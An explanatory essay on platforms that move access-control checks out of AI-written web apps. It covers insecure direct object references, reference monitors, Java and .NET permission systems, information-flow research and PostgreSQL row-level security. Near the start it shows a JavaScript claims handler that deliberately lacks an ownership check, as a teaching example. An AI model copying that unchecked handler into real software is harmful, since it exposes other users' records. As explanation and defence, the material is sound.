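# Platforms that keep security-critical logic out of AI-written software

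## What it means to take security checks out of application code

Most web applications contain their own security checks. The program that draws the page and queries the database also controls who may see what, so one forgotten check can show a customer's records to a stranger. Several hosting systems of 2025 and 2026, built for AI-written software, handle these checks themselves. The AI still writes the application, but the *platform*, meaning the hosting system that runs the code and enforces rules on it from outside, determines who is logged in, which data each person may reach and what the program can connect to. Cloudflare's *Enterprise AI Vibe Coding Platform*, a design guide from a web infrastructure company, treats AI-generated code as untrusted and therefore places protection "at the platform level, not the code level".

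The demand comes from *vibe coding*, which means building software by describing it to an AI, with little or no human reading of the code. The AI researcher Andrej Karpathy introduced the term in February 2025. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (Jha, Anand and colleagues, 2026) describes how vibe coding has since broadened to include people with little or no programming experience, who publish whole applications through conversation alone. Someone who cannot read code will not notice that a security check is missing from it. The paper also cites an audit of 200 vibe-coded applications in which more than 90% had at least one vulnerability.

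### Claim 417

Suppose an office manager asks an AI for an app in which employees file expense claims. Among much else, the AI produces a handler, the piece of code that answers one kind of request. This one answers requests to view a claim:

```js
app.get("/claims/:id", async (req, res) => {
  if (!req.user) return res.status(401).send("Please log in");

  const result = await db.query(
    "SELECT * FROM claims WHERE id = $1", [req.params.id]);

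  res.json(result.rows[0]);
});
```

The line that begins with `if` rejects any visitor who has not logged in. This is *authentication*, which establishes who is making a request. After this check, the server can treat the visitor as Ana from the sales team. The remaining lines fetch the claim whose number appears in the web address and send it back. The handler lacks *authorization*, which decides whether the person or program making a request is allowed to do what it asks for. In this case, it would decide whether Ana may read this particular claim. Ana filed claim 416, but if she changes the number in her address bar to 417, the server sends her Ben's hotel bill.

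*Preventing Web Application Access Control Abuse*, a joint advisory from the Australian Cyber Security Centre and two US agencies, calls this flaw an "insecure direct object reference". The flaw is number 639 in the standard catalogue of software weaknesses. GCVE's *Authorization Bypass Through User-Controlled Key*, an entry in a public vulnerability database, links 5,432 reported vulnerabilities to that number.

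Testing tends to miss errors that open an unwanted path to data. Saltzer and Schroeder (1975) explained in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* that these errors go unnoticed in normal use because normal users do not try improper paths. The office manager who tries out the expense app clicks on her own claims, sees them, and concludes that the app works.

A filter in front of the app will not catch Ana's request either, because it is well formed and comes from a real employee with a valid login. The request is wrong only because claim 417 belongs to Ben, and in a conventional app that fact has meaning only inside the application. WaterISAC's *CISA and Partners Release Joint Cybersecurity Advisory* (2023), a summary of the agencies' warning, describes flaws that allow such requests as "hard to prevent outside the development process". Any platform that blocks her request needs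 some way to determine who owns the claim.

### One request, three designs

The obvious fix keeps the check in the application. The AI, or a programmer, changes the query to read `WHERE id = $1 AND owner_id = $2` and supplies Ana's identity as the second value. Ana's request for 417 then returns nothing. But an expense app has many handlers, including ones that edit claims, delete them, search, export to a spreadsheet or show scanned receipts, and each needs its own version of the extra condition. When the manager asks for a new feature, the AI writes more handlers and could leave the condition out of any of them.

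Alternatively, the database can do the checking. With row-level security, a rule attached to the claims table lets a user read a row only if that user owns it, and the database applies the rule to every query. The faulty handler above stays the same. When it requests claim 417, the database finds that the current user is Ana and the owner is Ben, so it returns no row. The rule is a *policy*, a statement of who may do what, and the database engine is the mechanism that enforces it. Another example of a policy is "Employees read their own claims and managers read their team's." This arrangement depends on the database having a reliable way to identify the current user. Ana can still get Ben's hotel bill if the handler can simply declare that the current user is Ben, or if it connects with an administrator's password that bypasses the rule.

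A more radical design removes the need for the app to check who owns a claim. The platform gives each employee a separate copy of the expense app with its own database, and checks the user's identity before any generated code runs. Ana's request for claim 417 goes to her copy, which has no such claim. This relies on *isolation*, which means keeping one program or customer from reading or changing what belongs to another, as when two companies rent space on one server and neither can open the other's files. In *Gadgets*, Varda (2026) demonstrated the idea with a slide editor in which each deck is its own instance of the app. The editor's code doesn't need to check which decks a visitor may open, since each instance holds only one.

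Complete isolation between users doesn't work for an expense system, because a manager has to approve claims from twelve people and the finance department wants a total for the quarter. Saltzer and Schroeder remarked that the user of a system offering only isolation might as well have a private computer. An expense system has to let selected data pass between users, which brings back the questions of authorization, though in fewer places and, if the platform is well built, outside the generated code.

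### The handler as a confused deputy

What went wrong with claim 417 can also be seen as a misuse of the handler's authority. The handler has to serve every employee, so its database password opens the whole claims table. Ana has no such password, but she gets access to Ben's claim by having the handler use its password for her.

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) gave this kind of failure its name and illustrated it with an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates other programs, had permission to write files in a system directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. Users could ask the compiler to write debugging output to a file of their choice, and one of them entered the name of the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the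 compiler had permission to write in that directory, and the billing information was lost.

A *confused deputy* is a program tricked into using its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. Hardy looked for the faulty line of code and could not find one. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct when its author wrote it, and became wrong later, when somebody else gave the compiler a new permission. The engineers then added a system call that let a program select which of its two authorities to use, but they soon met applications that needed more than two. At one point the conditions for opening a file took fourteen "ands" and "ors" to write down.

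Hardy's preferred solution was the *capability*, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and carries permission to use it. The compiler would hold one capability for the statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output file. A user without a capability for the billing file could not make the compiler write to it by typing its name. Rajani, Garg and Rezk later proved in a formal setting, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, that capability systems and ordinary access control are fundamentally different. They also precisely defined what it means for a program to be free of confused deputy attacks.

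In the expense app, the platform would withhold the database connection and pass the handler an object, say `myClaims`, that can reach only Ana's claims. The handler could then safely call `myClaims.get(417)` without an ownership check. But this works only if the platform grants a narrow capability. If it gives the app one capability for the entire table, the app is a confused deputy again.

### The reference monitor and its three tests

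The theory behind this approach comes from the US Air Force. Around 1970 it wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them would be writing their own programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported the conclusions of a panel that assumed the worst case, in which a user with legitimate access to the machine writes a program to attack it. The defence had to be in whatever controlled the programs as they ran, because reading every such program in advance would not solve the problem.

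Anderson's term for it was the *reference monitor*, a mechanism that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the user behind it may do. He set three tests for any real implementation:

- It must always be invoked. If some programs escape the check, those programs become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same standard.
- It must be tamper-proof, since a check that the attacker can alter protects nothing.
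- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Otherwise nobody can know that the other two conditions hold.

Anderson applied the tests to GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the time. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but programs read and wrote files by calling the operating system, most of which ran with the memory check switched off. The operating system itself did not qualify as the monitor either, because it had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify, and several teams had already broken into it.

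The ownership check in the AI-written handler does worse than GCOS III. It runs only in the handlers where the AI included it, the AI can delete it at the next prompt, and the amount of code to verify grows with every feature. A check in the database or the platform can pass the invocation and tampering tests, as long as the generated code has no other way to reach the data. Anderson set the same condition when he suggested building a monitor into a database query system, which would work if users could do nothing except query.

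The size requirement is harder to meet. The *trusted computing base* is all the code and configuration that must be correct for the guarantee to hold. When the database does the checking, the expense app's trusted computing base includes the database engine, the ownership rule and the login service, but not the handler. Modern database engines are much larger than GCOS III was, so by Anderson's standard these platforms fail, or at least nobody has shown that they pass. They offer a weaker assurance that is still worth having, because thousands of customers rely on the same engine and its makers keep repairing it, whereas the AI has only just written the handler and perhaps nobody has read it.

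The login service is on that list because Anderson's monitor depends on other parts of the system to identify every user correctly first. If a platform lets Ana log in as Ben, she can reach Ben's data even when the ownership checks work perfectly.

Two of Saltzer and Schroeder's design principles describe what the monitor should enforce. Under *least privilege*, every program runs with the smallest set of permissions that its job requires, which limits the damage from an accident or error. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, Anderson (1972) had similarly asked that a program working for a user get only that user's access, even if the program belongs to the operating system. Under *fail-safe defaults*, access is refused unless a rule grants it, which makes mistakes easier to notice. If someone forgets to grant Ana access to her own claims, she soon complains. In a system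 that allows access by default, someone could forget to block her from Ben's claims, and the hole can stay open for years because the app seems to work.

### Who checks, who writes the rule, and whether the code can get round it

Vendors describe their platforms in very different vocabularies, and most of the differences that matter come down to three questions. Who runs the check? Who writes the rule? Can generated code bypass it? For claim 417 the answers look like this:

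| Design | Who runs the check | Who writes the rule | Can generated code bypass it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The app checks | The generated handler | The AI, anew in each handler | Yes, by omitting a line |
| The database checks | The database | Whoever defines the rule on the table, possibly the AI again | Yes, if it holds an exempt password or can choose the current user |
| One instance per person | The platform, before the app runs | Whoever shares the instance | Only through a fault in the platform or an over-broad grant |

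*Access Control Fundamentals*, a textbook chapter, treats the rules that specify access and the monitor that enforces them as separate parts of a system. Either can fail while the other works. If the AI writes a database rule that lets any logged-in employee read any claim, the database will apply that rule to every query, and Ana will be able to read Ben's hotel claim.

### Prompts, scanners and reviewers

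Most work on the security of AI-written code tries to get better checks into the code. One approach is to prompt the model to write secure code, but according to *The Illusion of Secure LLM Code* (2026), earlier studies found that such prompting alone does not consistently remove weaknesses across tasks and models. Another is to scan the code. *VibeGuard* (2026) proposes a scan that the AI assistant calls before it publishes anything and a second, compulsory scan before release, so that catching packaging mistakes, such as shipping files that should have stayed private, does not depend on the developer reading the code. A third approach is to have a person review the code, but vibe coding more or less means that nobody does.

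These methods find real flaws, and Cloudflare's guide keeps scans and human review in its release process. But the check is still in the generated code, so the next edit can remove it. Authorization also poses its own problem, because the program alone doesn't show whether a missing ownership test is a mistake. If the handler for claim 417 returned lunch menus instead of claims, the same code would be correct, since every employee may read every menu. Whether the test is needed depends on a policy that may be known only to the office manager.

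A clean result doesn't prove much either. Anderson argued that the "tiger teams" the military employed to break into its own computers could reveal flaws, but that when they found none, the security of the system was still unknown.

### Removing a flaw and limiting its harm

Some techniques make a class of mistake impossible. Cloudflare gives the example of memory-safe programming languages such as Rust, which rule out buffer overflows before the program runs. In a buffer overflow, a program writes past the end of its allotted memory. Platform checks mostly leave mistakes in the code but prevent their consequences. The handler for claim 417 has the same mistake after the move as before, but the mistake no longer makes a difference to Ben.

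Varda let an AI agent extend his slide editor, and the agent added a field for pasting in drawings in a format that can also carry executable script. This may well be a common kind of security hole, but Varda left it in place because the platform confines the whole app, so a malicious script could not communicate with anything outside it. His statement in the talk that security bugs in such code do not matter is too strong. A script inside Ana's copy of the expense app could still alter or delete her expense claims, and the confinement depends on the platform's isolation and on which connections someone has granted to the app.

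Some mistakes get past all of these designs. Suppose the AI writes a handler that lets employees approve expense claims but doesn't check whether they are approving their own. Ana files a claim and then approves it. She is logged in, the claim is hers, and it sits in her own copy of the app, so neither the ownership rule nor the isolation between instances stops her. Preventing this takes a rule about approvals, written by someone who knows how the company handles expenses.

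## 1995–2025: Java, .NET and the permission checks that were withdrawn

Programmers handed part of their security work to platforms long before vibe coding. Sun Microsystems introduced Java in 1995, and Microsoft followed with .NET in 2002. Both are *managed runtimes*, layers of software that load a program, supply its memory and can refuse its requests. They stopped programs from corrupting memory and checked whether a given piece of code had permission to open a file or connect to the network. The memory protection is still in use, but Java's maintainers permanently disabled the permission checks in 2025, and Microsoft left them out of the current versions of .NET.

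### How Java prevents memory errors

In a language such as C, a program can overflow a buffer or keep using memory after freeing it, and an attacker who controls the data can often exploit these errors to take over the program. C programmers have to guard against such errors at every array access, much as the AI has to include the ownership test in every handler of the expense app.

A Java compiler produces *bytecode*, a set of about 200 simple instructions for an imaginary machine, and the runtime carries them out. Bytecode has no instruction for reading an arbitrary memory address. A program can reach an object only through a reference that it got from the runtime. To make sure that a downloaded program respects this, the runtime first *verifies* its bytecode. Leroy, in *Java bytecode verification*, describes the usual method, in which the verifier steps through the code without any real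 data and keeps track only of the type of each value. Suppose somebody writes bytecode by hand to pass off the number 5 as a reference to an expense claim:

```
iconst_5               // the verifier records: an integer
getfield Claim.owner   // needs a reference to a Claim
```

The second instruction reads a field of a claim, so it needs a reference to a claim. The verifier has recorded an integer instead, so it rejects the code before any of it runs. Where two branches of a program meet, the verifier keeps only the type information that holds for both. If one branch leaves an integer in a slot and the other leaves an object reference, the verifier treats the slot as uninitialised and rejects any later attempt to read it.

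Some errors depend on values that are known only when the program runs, so the runtime compares every array index with the length of the array and raises an error if the index is out of range. The programmer's mistake is still there, but it can no longer overwrite other data. The runtime also uses *garbage collection*, which reclaims an object's memory only when the program can no longer reach the object, so no reference can lead to memory that now holds something else.

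The programmer gets all of this without writing any code for it, so can't leave it out by mistake. An attacker gains nothing by writing bytecode by hand or using a malicious compiler, because the verifier examines the bytecode itself. Nothing needs to be configured either, because no program has a legitimate reason to read past the end of an array, and the same rule suits a game and a payroll system. The rule about who may read claim 417, by contrast, is specific to one company.

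### Where memory safety ends

The guarantee depends on the runtime being correct. Leroy warns that any bug that lets badly typed code through the verifier could allow an attack. In *Improving the official specification of Java bytecode verification*, Coglio (2003) found that the specification itself was inadequate in places, so a programmer who followed it could build a verifier with security holes.

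Java programs can also call *native code*, usually written in C or C++, which the verifier doesn't examine, and Java has a few interfaces that bypass its normal rules. *JEP draft* (Pressler, Buckley and Reinhold, 2023), one of the proposals through which Java's developers announce changes, gives the example of a counter that should only hold even numbers. The counter keeps its number in a private field and has methods that add or subtract two. Ordinary code cannot make the number odd, but a library that uses "deep reflection", a way of changing private fields from outside, can set it to 3. Native code and an interface called `sun.misc.Unsafe` can also break memory safety.

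For most of Java's history, a library could opt out of the guarantees for the whole program, perhaps without the application's developer knowing the library was there. Since Java 9, the maintainers have been gradually restricting the interfaces that allow this. They aim to let a library use them only if the application's developer allows it when starting the runtime.

None of this protects Ben, because a Java version of the expense handler could pass verification, stay within the bounds of every array and still send his hotel bill to Ana.

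### Permissions for each source of code

Most early uses of Java involved *applets*, according to Inside Java's *So Long and Thanks for All the Applets* (2025). Applets were small programs that a web page delivered to the visitor's browser. Memory safety kept an applet from tampering with the browser's memory, but the applet could still use Java's libraries to delete a file. In Java 1.0 the libraries therefore called a component named the *Security Manager* before any such operation. It approved requests from programs installed on the computer and rejected those from applets.

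*Understanding Java Stack Inspection* (Wallach and Felten, 1998) explains that these checks depend on memory safety. An applet cannot forge references or access a library's private data, so it has to use the few entry points that contain the checks. This is how Java tried to meet Anderson's condition that a program must not be able to bypass the reference monitor.

Two levels of trust soon proved too coarse. Java 1.1 let publishers sign their applets, and an applet whose signature the computer recognised got the same access as an installed program. Java 1.2 replaced this with a detailed policy, which Gong and Schemers (1998), in *Implementing Protection Domains in the Java Development Kit 1.2*, describe from the inside, as two of Sun's own engineers. The user or an administrator listed the permissions for each *code source*, meaning the web address that the code came from and the keys that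 signed it. An entry for an applet that draws charts might look like this:

```
grant codeBase "http://charts.example/" {
  permission java.io.FilePermission "/tmp/*", "read,write";
};
```

Applets from this address could use files in the temporary directory but no others. The same scheme could also restrict installed programs, to limit the damage if one had a flaw.

### A call stack, from the newest call to the oldest

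A running program mixes code from several sources. The chart applet might call a library, which calls Java's own file code, which has permission to open anything. If the runtime looked only at the code that made the final request, the applet could borrow the file code's permissions, as the user at Tymshare borrowed the compiler's. Java therefore used *stack inspection*. The call stack is the runtime's record of which method called which, and the runtime searched it before each sensitive operation. Suppose the applet asks a report library on Ana's computer to load a file that contains her salary:

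| Call, newest first | Where the code came from | May it read the salary file? |
|---|---|---|
| `FileInputStream` opens the file | Java itself | Yes |
| `ReportLibrary.load` | Installed on Ana's computer | Yes |
| `Chart.draw` | Applet from charts.example | No, so the runtime raises an error |

The file code and the report library both have permission, but the applet doesn't, so the request fails. A chain of calls has only the permissions that all the code in it holds. A new thread inherits the call history of the thread that started it, so the applet cannot avoid the check by starting one.

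This rule is sometimes too strict. If the applet asks for the local time, Java's time library has to read a time-zone file that the applet isn't allowed to open. The library can declare that it takes responsibility for the request, using a call eventually named `doPrivileged`. The search then goes from the file code to the time library, finds that the library has permission and has made the declaration, and stops there and allows the request. The applet could make the same declaration but would gain nothing, because the runtime tests each method's own permissions before it looks for a declaration.

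This is safe as long as the applet cannot influence which file the time library opens. A library that made the declaration and then opened any file its caller named would be a confused deputy. Stack inspection thus confined the problem to the libraries that used `doPrivileged`, whose developers had to get it right each time. Wallach and Felten report that when a search reached the oldest call without finding either a declaration or a missing permission, Netscape's browser refused access, while Sun's and Microsoft's versions of Java allowed it.

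### Code Access Security in .NET

Microsoft built a similar mechanism, *Code Access Security*, into .NET. The runtime determined the permissions of each assembly, a unit of compiled code, from its origin and publisher, using a policy set by the machine's administrator. When the code attempted something sensitive, the runtime searched the call stack. In *Security in .NET*, Box argued that permissions should depend on where code came from because people installed so much of it over the internet, and even a trusted user couldn't tell whether it was safe.

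Administrators struggled with the policy. Dai (2009), in *Exploring the .NET Framework 4 Security Model*, an article in Microsoft's developer magazine, called it "extremely difficult to get right". Programs stopped working when people moved them to a shared network drive, because the runtime then assigned them a different origin. Anyone who had written an elaborate policy for .NET 1.1 had to redo it by hand for version 2.0. The policy also did not apply to native programs, which users started in the same way and couldn't tell apart from .NET programs.

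Developers also had trouble with `Deny`, a method that seemed to let a program withhold a permission from the code it was about to call. `Deny` only left a mark on the call stack, and the called code could use `Assert`, .NET's counterpart to `doPrivileged`, to end the search before it reached that mark. Dai concluded that using `Deny` was always a security hole.

### Why the maintainers gave up

Microsoft withdrew its permission checks in stages. Version 4 of the .NET Framework switched off the machine-wide policy by default but kept a simpler sandbox, in which all the untrusted code in one compartment had the same permissions. Microsoft later gave up on the sandbox too, explaining that code could raise its own privileges in too many cases and that the checks complicated the runtime even for applications that didn't use them. In *How to*, a guide to running partly trusted code, Microsoft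 warns that it will not patch any further escapes from the sandbox.

Java's maintainers put more weight on lack of use. They announced their plan to remove the Security Manager in *JEP 411* (2021), a proposal from OpenJDK, the project that develops Java. The Security Manager was originally meant for applets, which Java no longer supported. For other programs it had always been off by default, partly because the stack searches were slow, and only a handful of applications came with a policy. It also could not address 19 of the 25 kinds of flaw on a 2020 industry list of the most dangerous.

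The proposal also explains why so few developers wrote policies. Someone who only wanted to limit which directory a program could read from had to list every other permission the program needed, since the policy language had no way to express "everything except". Stack inspection added to the work, because if a library needed network access, the application that called it needed the same permission unless the library's author had used `doPrivileged` correctly. Developers often granted all permissions because it was easier.

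The maintainers had to keep the checks working whether or not anyone switched them on. Mullan and Buckley (2024), in *JEP 486*, counted more than 1,000 methods that had to check permissions and more than 1,200 that had to raise their own privileges, as some in the time library do. About 4,000 tests covered the feature. Their proposal permanently disabled the Security Manager in Java 24, released in March 2025, and let the maintainers delete over 50,000 lines of code.

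Some developers objected. *Discuss JEP 411*, a campaign website, argued that most programs don't need everything Java can do, that each unneeded ability gives an attacker something to use, and that OpenJDK was offering no replacement. In *JEP proposed to target JDK 24*, a mailing-list exchange with Buckley (2024), a developer asked for a way to run a plug-in that could not start new threads and could open files only in one directory. Mullan and Buckley judged the demand for such limits to be tiny based on their own experience and how little discussion the warnings in Java 17 had caused, not on a survey. They also mentioned that projects such as the Tomcat web server had dropped support for the Security Manager, which is weak evidence because those projects already knew it was going away.

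Java's treatment of old programs is closer to the principle of fail-safe defaults than .NET's. Java 24 will not start with the Security Manager enabled, and its old check methods always raise an error. In .NET 5 and later, according to Microsoft's *SYSLIB0003*, every leftover permission demand succeeds, so a program that still relies on one runs without that protection.

### Browsers and phones kept their permissions

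Memory safety, which needs no configuration, has lasted, while the Security Manager, which needed a correct policy for each program, was withdrawn. This pattern may not hold for other security guarantees. If it did, a platform for AI-written code should enforce only rules that are identical for every app.

Java and .NET withdrew their permission checks, but browsers and phones still give different programs different permissions, and people use these every day. A web page needs permission to use the camera, and a phone app needs permission to read the owner's location.

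I think the most important difference is probably when developers meet the restrictions.

Phones always enforce app permissions, so a developer whose app lacks one finds out the first time they test it. Java developers wrote and tested their libraries with the Security Manager off, so anyone who later turned it on had to work out which permissions each library needed.

The boundary is also simpler because it surrounds the whole app. When a phone grants a map app location access, nobody has to work out permissions along a chain of calls between the app's libraries. The operating system does the checking, so the programming language doesn't matter. UWP apps, a restricted type of Windows app, cannot read or write arbitrary files whether they are written in C# or C++, according to a separately published addendum to the programming handbook C# 7.0 in a Nutshell.

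The maintainers of Java and .NET still favor restricting programs, but by other means. Mullan and Buckley recommend containers and operating-system sandboxes, which they describe as widely adopted and relatively easy to use, and Microsoft gives similar advice. Serverless hosts later separated each customer's code using V8 isolates or small virtual machines. Somebody has to configure these systems too, so the need for a policy cannot by itself explain why the Security Manager failed. Its policies were also long and divided a program into many parts, and most developers never had to make their code work under them.

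AI might make long policies less of a burden. OpenJDK mentions a lack of tools for working out which permissions a program needs, and an AI could draft such a list quickly. But if it derives the list from code it has just written, the list will permit whatever the code does, including anything it does by mistake.

Even a perfect policy of this kind would not have kept Ben's hotel bill from Ana. Java and .NET gave permissions to code according to its origin, and all the employees use the same code. Java later added an interface for permissions that depend on the user, but the expense app's author would still have had to define a permission for claims and call the check in every handler. An operating system can stop the app from contacting unknown servers, but it has to let the app reach its database, and it cannot tell claim 416 from claim 417 because both are bytes in the same connection.

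## 2007–2022: Frameworks and databases that enforce data rules beneath the application

A database or web framework can distinguish claim 416 from claim 417, which an operating system can't do. From 2007 onwards, several research groups used these layers to protect data from mistakes in web applications, and some also wanted to protect it from applications written by an attacker. Their systems keep the rule about who may see a claim in one place and apply it to whatever the application does. None of these systems came into wide use, but row-level security, a simpler feature built into databases, did.

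### Labels that follow the data

An ownership check protects a claim only when the handler fetches it. The code can then copy the claim into an email, a saved page or a spreadsheet. *Information flow control* covers these later steps by attaching a *label* to each piece of data that specifies who may receive it. Code that reads the data takes on its label, and the runtime blocks that code from sending output to anyone the label excludes.

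Suppose Maria manages both Ana and Ben. Claim 416 carries the label "Ana or Maria" and claim 417 the label "Ben or Maria". Ana opens a page, and the faulty handler reads both claims:

| Step | Who may now receive the handler's output |
|---|---|
| Ana's request arrives | Anyone |
| The handler reads claim 416 | Ana or Maria |
| The handler reads claim 417 | Maria, or Ana and Ben together |

After the second read, a recipient has to satisfy both labels, "(Ana or Maria) and (Ben or Maria)", which reduces to "Maria, or Ana and Ben together". Ana alone doesn't satisfy that, so the runtime blocks the page even though the handler contains no ownership check.

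It would also block the page if the handler had read claim 417 but put nothing from it on the page. This is *over-labelling*, where a label restricts output that reveals nothing secret. A runtime can reduce over-labelling by tracking only copied text, but then it misses indirect leaks. For example, if the handler turns the page red whenever Ben's bill exceeds 1,000 euros, Ana learns something about the bill even though the handler copied no text from it.

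Applications sometimes need *declassification*, the deliberate release of labelled data. For example, the finance department wants the total for the quarter, but code that adds up all the claims gets a label that restricts its output to people entitled to read every claim. A trusted routine therefore computes the total and gives it a new label, "Finance". That routine becomes part of the trusted computing base, because no lower layer will catch the mistake if it releases the list of claims instead of the total.

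### Buggy code and hostile code

Adapting a program to labels can take a lot of work. Flume, a system from 2007, tracked labels between operating-system processes, so programmers had to split an application into components with different privileges. Yip, Wang and colleagues report in *Improving Application Security with Data Flow Assertions* that protecting the pages of a wiki program called MoinMoin took about 2,000 lines of new or changed code with Flume and 23 lines with their own system, RESIN (2009).

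RESIN is a modified version of the PHP and Python runtimes. A programmer writes a rule, such as "only Ben and Maria may receive this claim," and attaches it to the data as a *policy object*. The runtime copies the object along with the data, character by character. When the application stores the data in a database, the PHP version saves the object in an extra column. Before text leaves in a web page or an email, the runtime runs the check in every policy object attached to it.

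One of the flaws RESIN stopped was in HotCRP, a program for running academic conferences. HotCRP could email users their forgotten passwords, and it had a preview mode that displayed outgoing emails in the browser instead of sending them. With preview mode on, anyone could request a reminder for another user and read that user's password on the screen. Each feature was harmless separately, so a reviewer could easily have approved both. RESIN's rule blocked the password because it was going to a browser rather than to its owner's email address.

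The rules stopped 22 flaws across 12 existing applications. Fourteen of these were already public, and the researchers knew about them when they wrote the rules, so they are weak evidence. The other eight are stronger evidence. Three of those were in add-ons to phpBB, a web forum, whose outside programmers had left out the forum's permission checks. An AI that adds a feature to an app without reading all of its code is in a similar position.

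RESIN does not catch indirect leaks such as the red page. It also lets out any data that has no policy object, so data is unprotected if a programmer forgets to write its rule. It offers no protection against malicious application code, since a hostile handler could remove the policy object from Ben's claim before sending it.

*Hails* (Giffin, Levy and colleagues, 2012) does not require that trust. The framework separates the modules that hold data and its rules from the code that produces pages, which anyone may write. It uses labels like those in the example above and can derive them from the data, so that a user's list of friends determines who may read her email address. Hails accepts only applications written in a safe subset of Haskell, a programming language whose types show whether a function can communicate with the outside world.

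The researchers used Hails to run GitStar, a public site for hosting source code. One of its untrusted components displays files with coloured syntax. Once the component has read a private file, it can send output only to people who may read that file, so a malicious version could not pass the file to the component's author. Hails also blocks code from reading data that could never be sent to the user who made the request. In the expense app, the attempt to read claim 417 for Ana would fail immediately, and the claim's label would not block the rest of her page.

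Four developers from outside the project who used Hails liked not having to scatter security checks through their code, and the rules made some of their bugs harmless. But most found the first version of the policy interface hard to learn, and one wrote a blog that leaked unpublished posts. That developer had marked the posts themselves as search keys, which Hails shows to any code that may read the collection. The researchers responded with a simpler policy language. They were also unhappy with the browser protection, which required every user to install an extension and still allowed a malicious page to trick someone into releasing data.

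### Substitute values and refused queries

When an application requests data the user isn't allowed to see, it can receive an error, as in RESIN and Hails, or a harmless substitute. *Precise, Dynamic Information Flow for Database-Backed Applications* (Yang, Hance and colleagues, 2015) presents Jacqueline, which returns substitutes and is based on the Python web framework Django. Each sensitive field has a secret value and a public one. For example, Ben and Maria might see "Hotel Adler" on claim 417, while everyone else sees "Private expense".

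Searches make it hard to keep a value hidden. If Ana searches for Hotel Adler and Ben's claim comes up, she learns where he stayed even if the name is blanked out. Jacqueline stores the full and blanked-out versions as separate database rows, runs the search on both, and gives each viewer only the results from the version they may see, so Ana's search finds nothing.

Carrying two versions of every value can make a program very slow. A page listing eight courses and their instructors took 64 seconds, but only 0.19 seconds after the researchers made the framework discard irrelevant versions as soon as it identified the viewer. Jacqueline also could not use the database's own functions for counting and adding, because they would have mixed secret and public values, so a quarterly total would need separate code.

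The researchers and two students built three applications with Jacqueline and used one, a conference manager, to run a real workshop. They compared the conference manager with an ordinary Django version, but did not count flaws. Someone auditing the rules had to read 200 lines of the Jacqueline version and 575 of the Django version. This advantage depends on honest programmers, because the secret values are in the program's memory and code can reach them by bypassing the official interface.

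Jacqueline's users had to adopt its way of writing programs. Zhang, Sheng and colleagues (2022), in *Blockaid*, tried to avoid this by placing a proxy between an existing application and its database. Blockaid blocks every query that it cannot prove to be allowed. Its policy is a list of *views*, which here are queries that define what the current user may see:

```sql
SELECT * FROM claims WHERE owner_id = ?MyUId
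```

Blockaid allows a query only if the views, together with the answers to earlier queries in the same request, completely determine its result. More exactly, it allows a new query Q only if Q(D1) = Q(D2) for every pair of databases D1 and D2 that look the same through every view and give the same answers to the earlier queries. The faulty handler's query for claim 417 fails this test because two databases could hold different versions of Ben's claim and still look identical to Ana.

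Blockaid also blocks the office manager's request for her own claim 416, because the handler has asked for it by number alone and nothing in the request so far shows that it belongs to her. This is useful because it would expose the missing check the first time she clicked on one of her own claims. Once the AI adds the ownership condition to the query, Blockaid allows it. The application still contains the checks, and Blockaid tests whether they are sufficient.

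No algorithm can decide this question for all possible queries. Blockaid runs several automated provers on each case and blocks the query if none finds a proof within five seconds. If one does, Blockaid saves the proof in a general form that usually applies to other users and records. Saved proofs cut the load time of an order page in Spree, an online shop program, from 39 seconds to 0.17.

The researchers also tested Blockaid on diaspora*, a social network, and Autolab, which manages university courses. While writing Autolab's policy, they found two flaws in its existing checks. In one, the course page hid an unreleased handout that students could download from the assignment page. Blockaid checks only reads, so it would not stop Ana from deleting claim 417. It also relies on the application to identify the user correctly.

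Policies were short in all four systems, and most pages loaded at a tolerable speed:

| System | Size of the policies | Running cost |
|---|---|---|
| RESIN | 6 to 32 lines per rule | 33% more processor time for a HotCRP page |
| Hails | 17 lines for a table of user profiles | 42% fewer requests per second than a Java server on a trivial page, but 28% more than PHP |
| Jacqueline | 106 lines for the conference manager, against 130 in Django | Almost none for single records, up to about 1.75 times slower for long lists |
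| Blockaid | 57 to 108 views per application, and 19 to 96 changed lines of code | 2–12% longer page loads once it has saved its proofs |

The line counts don't measure the work of deciding what the policies should allow. One researcher spent about a month on the Spree policy, largely because they had to work out the developers' intentions from the code. The researchers also forgot a condition in the Autolab policy, which for a while let an instructor on one course see the assignments of all other courses.

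### A row rule for claim 417

Michael Stonebraker and Eugene Wong described a simpler approach in 1974, in which the database adds the access rule to each query. Row-level security works in this way. Oracle and Microsoft have it in their commercial databases, and PostgreSQL, a widely used open-source database, gained it in version 9.5, released in 2016. For the expense app it takes two commands:

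```sql
ALTER TABLE claims ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY own_claims ON claims
  USING (owner_id = current_setting('app.user_id')::int);
```

The first command switches the feature on for the claims table, and the second attaches a policy to it. As PostgreSQL's *Row Security Policies* explains, the database tests the policy's condition on each row before it applies conditions from the user's query. Ana's request for claim 417 therefore returns no row. The policy also covers changes, so Ana can't edit Ben's claim or file one in his name. A second policy could let Maria read her team's claims. By default, PostgreSQL shows a row if any policy allows it.

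The examples in the manual identify people by `current_user`, the account logged in to the database. Web applications usually connect through one shared account rather than giving each visitor their own, so something has to tell the database which visitor each request is for. The policy above reads a session setting named `app.user_id`, and a sample policy in slicker.me's *PostgreSQL 18* uses the same technique to keep customers' data separate.

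The login layer sets this value before the handler runs. But any code that can send its own SQL commands over the connection can change it to Ben's number. To enforce the rule against generated code, a platform has to set the value itself and keep that code from sending arbitrary commands. It also has to reset the value between requests, or a reused connection might treat the next visitor as Ana.

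### Ways past the row rule

Row-level security is off by default for new tables. If the AI adds a table for scanned receipts without turning it on, every user of the shared account can read every receipt. Omissions of this kind later exposed data in apps made with Lovable, an AI app builder, on Supabase databases. Once row-level security is on, a table without a policy shows no rows. Turning it off again leaves the policies in place but inactive, so a person who checks only that a policy exists may think the table is safe.

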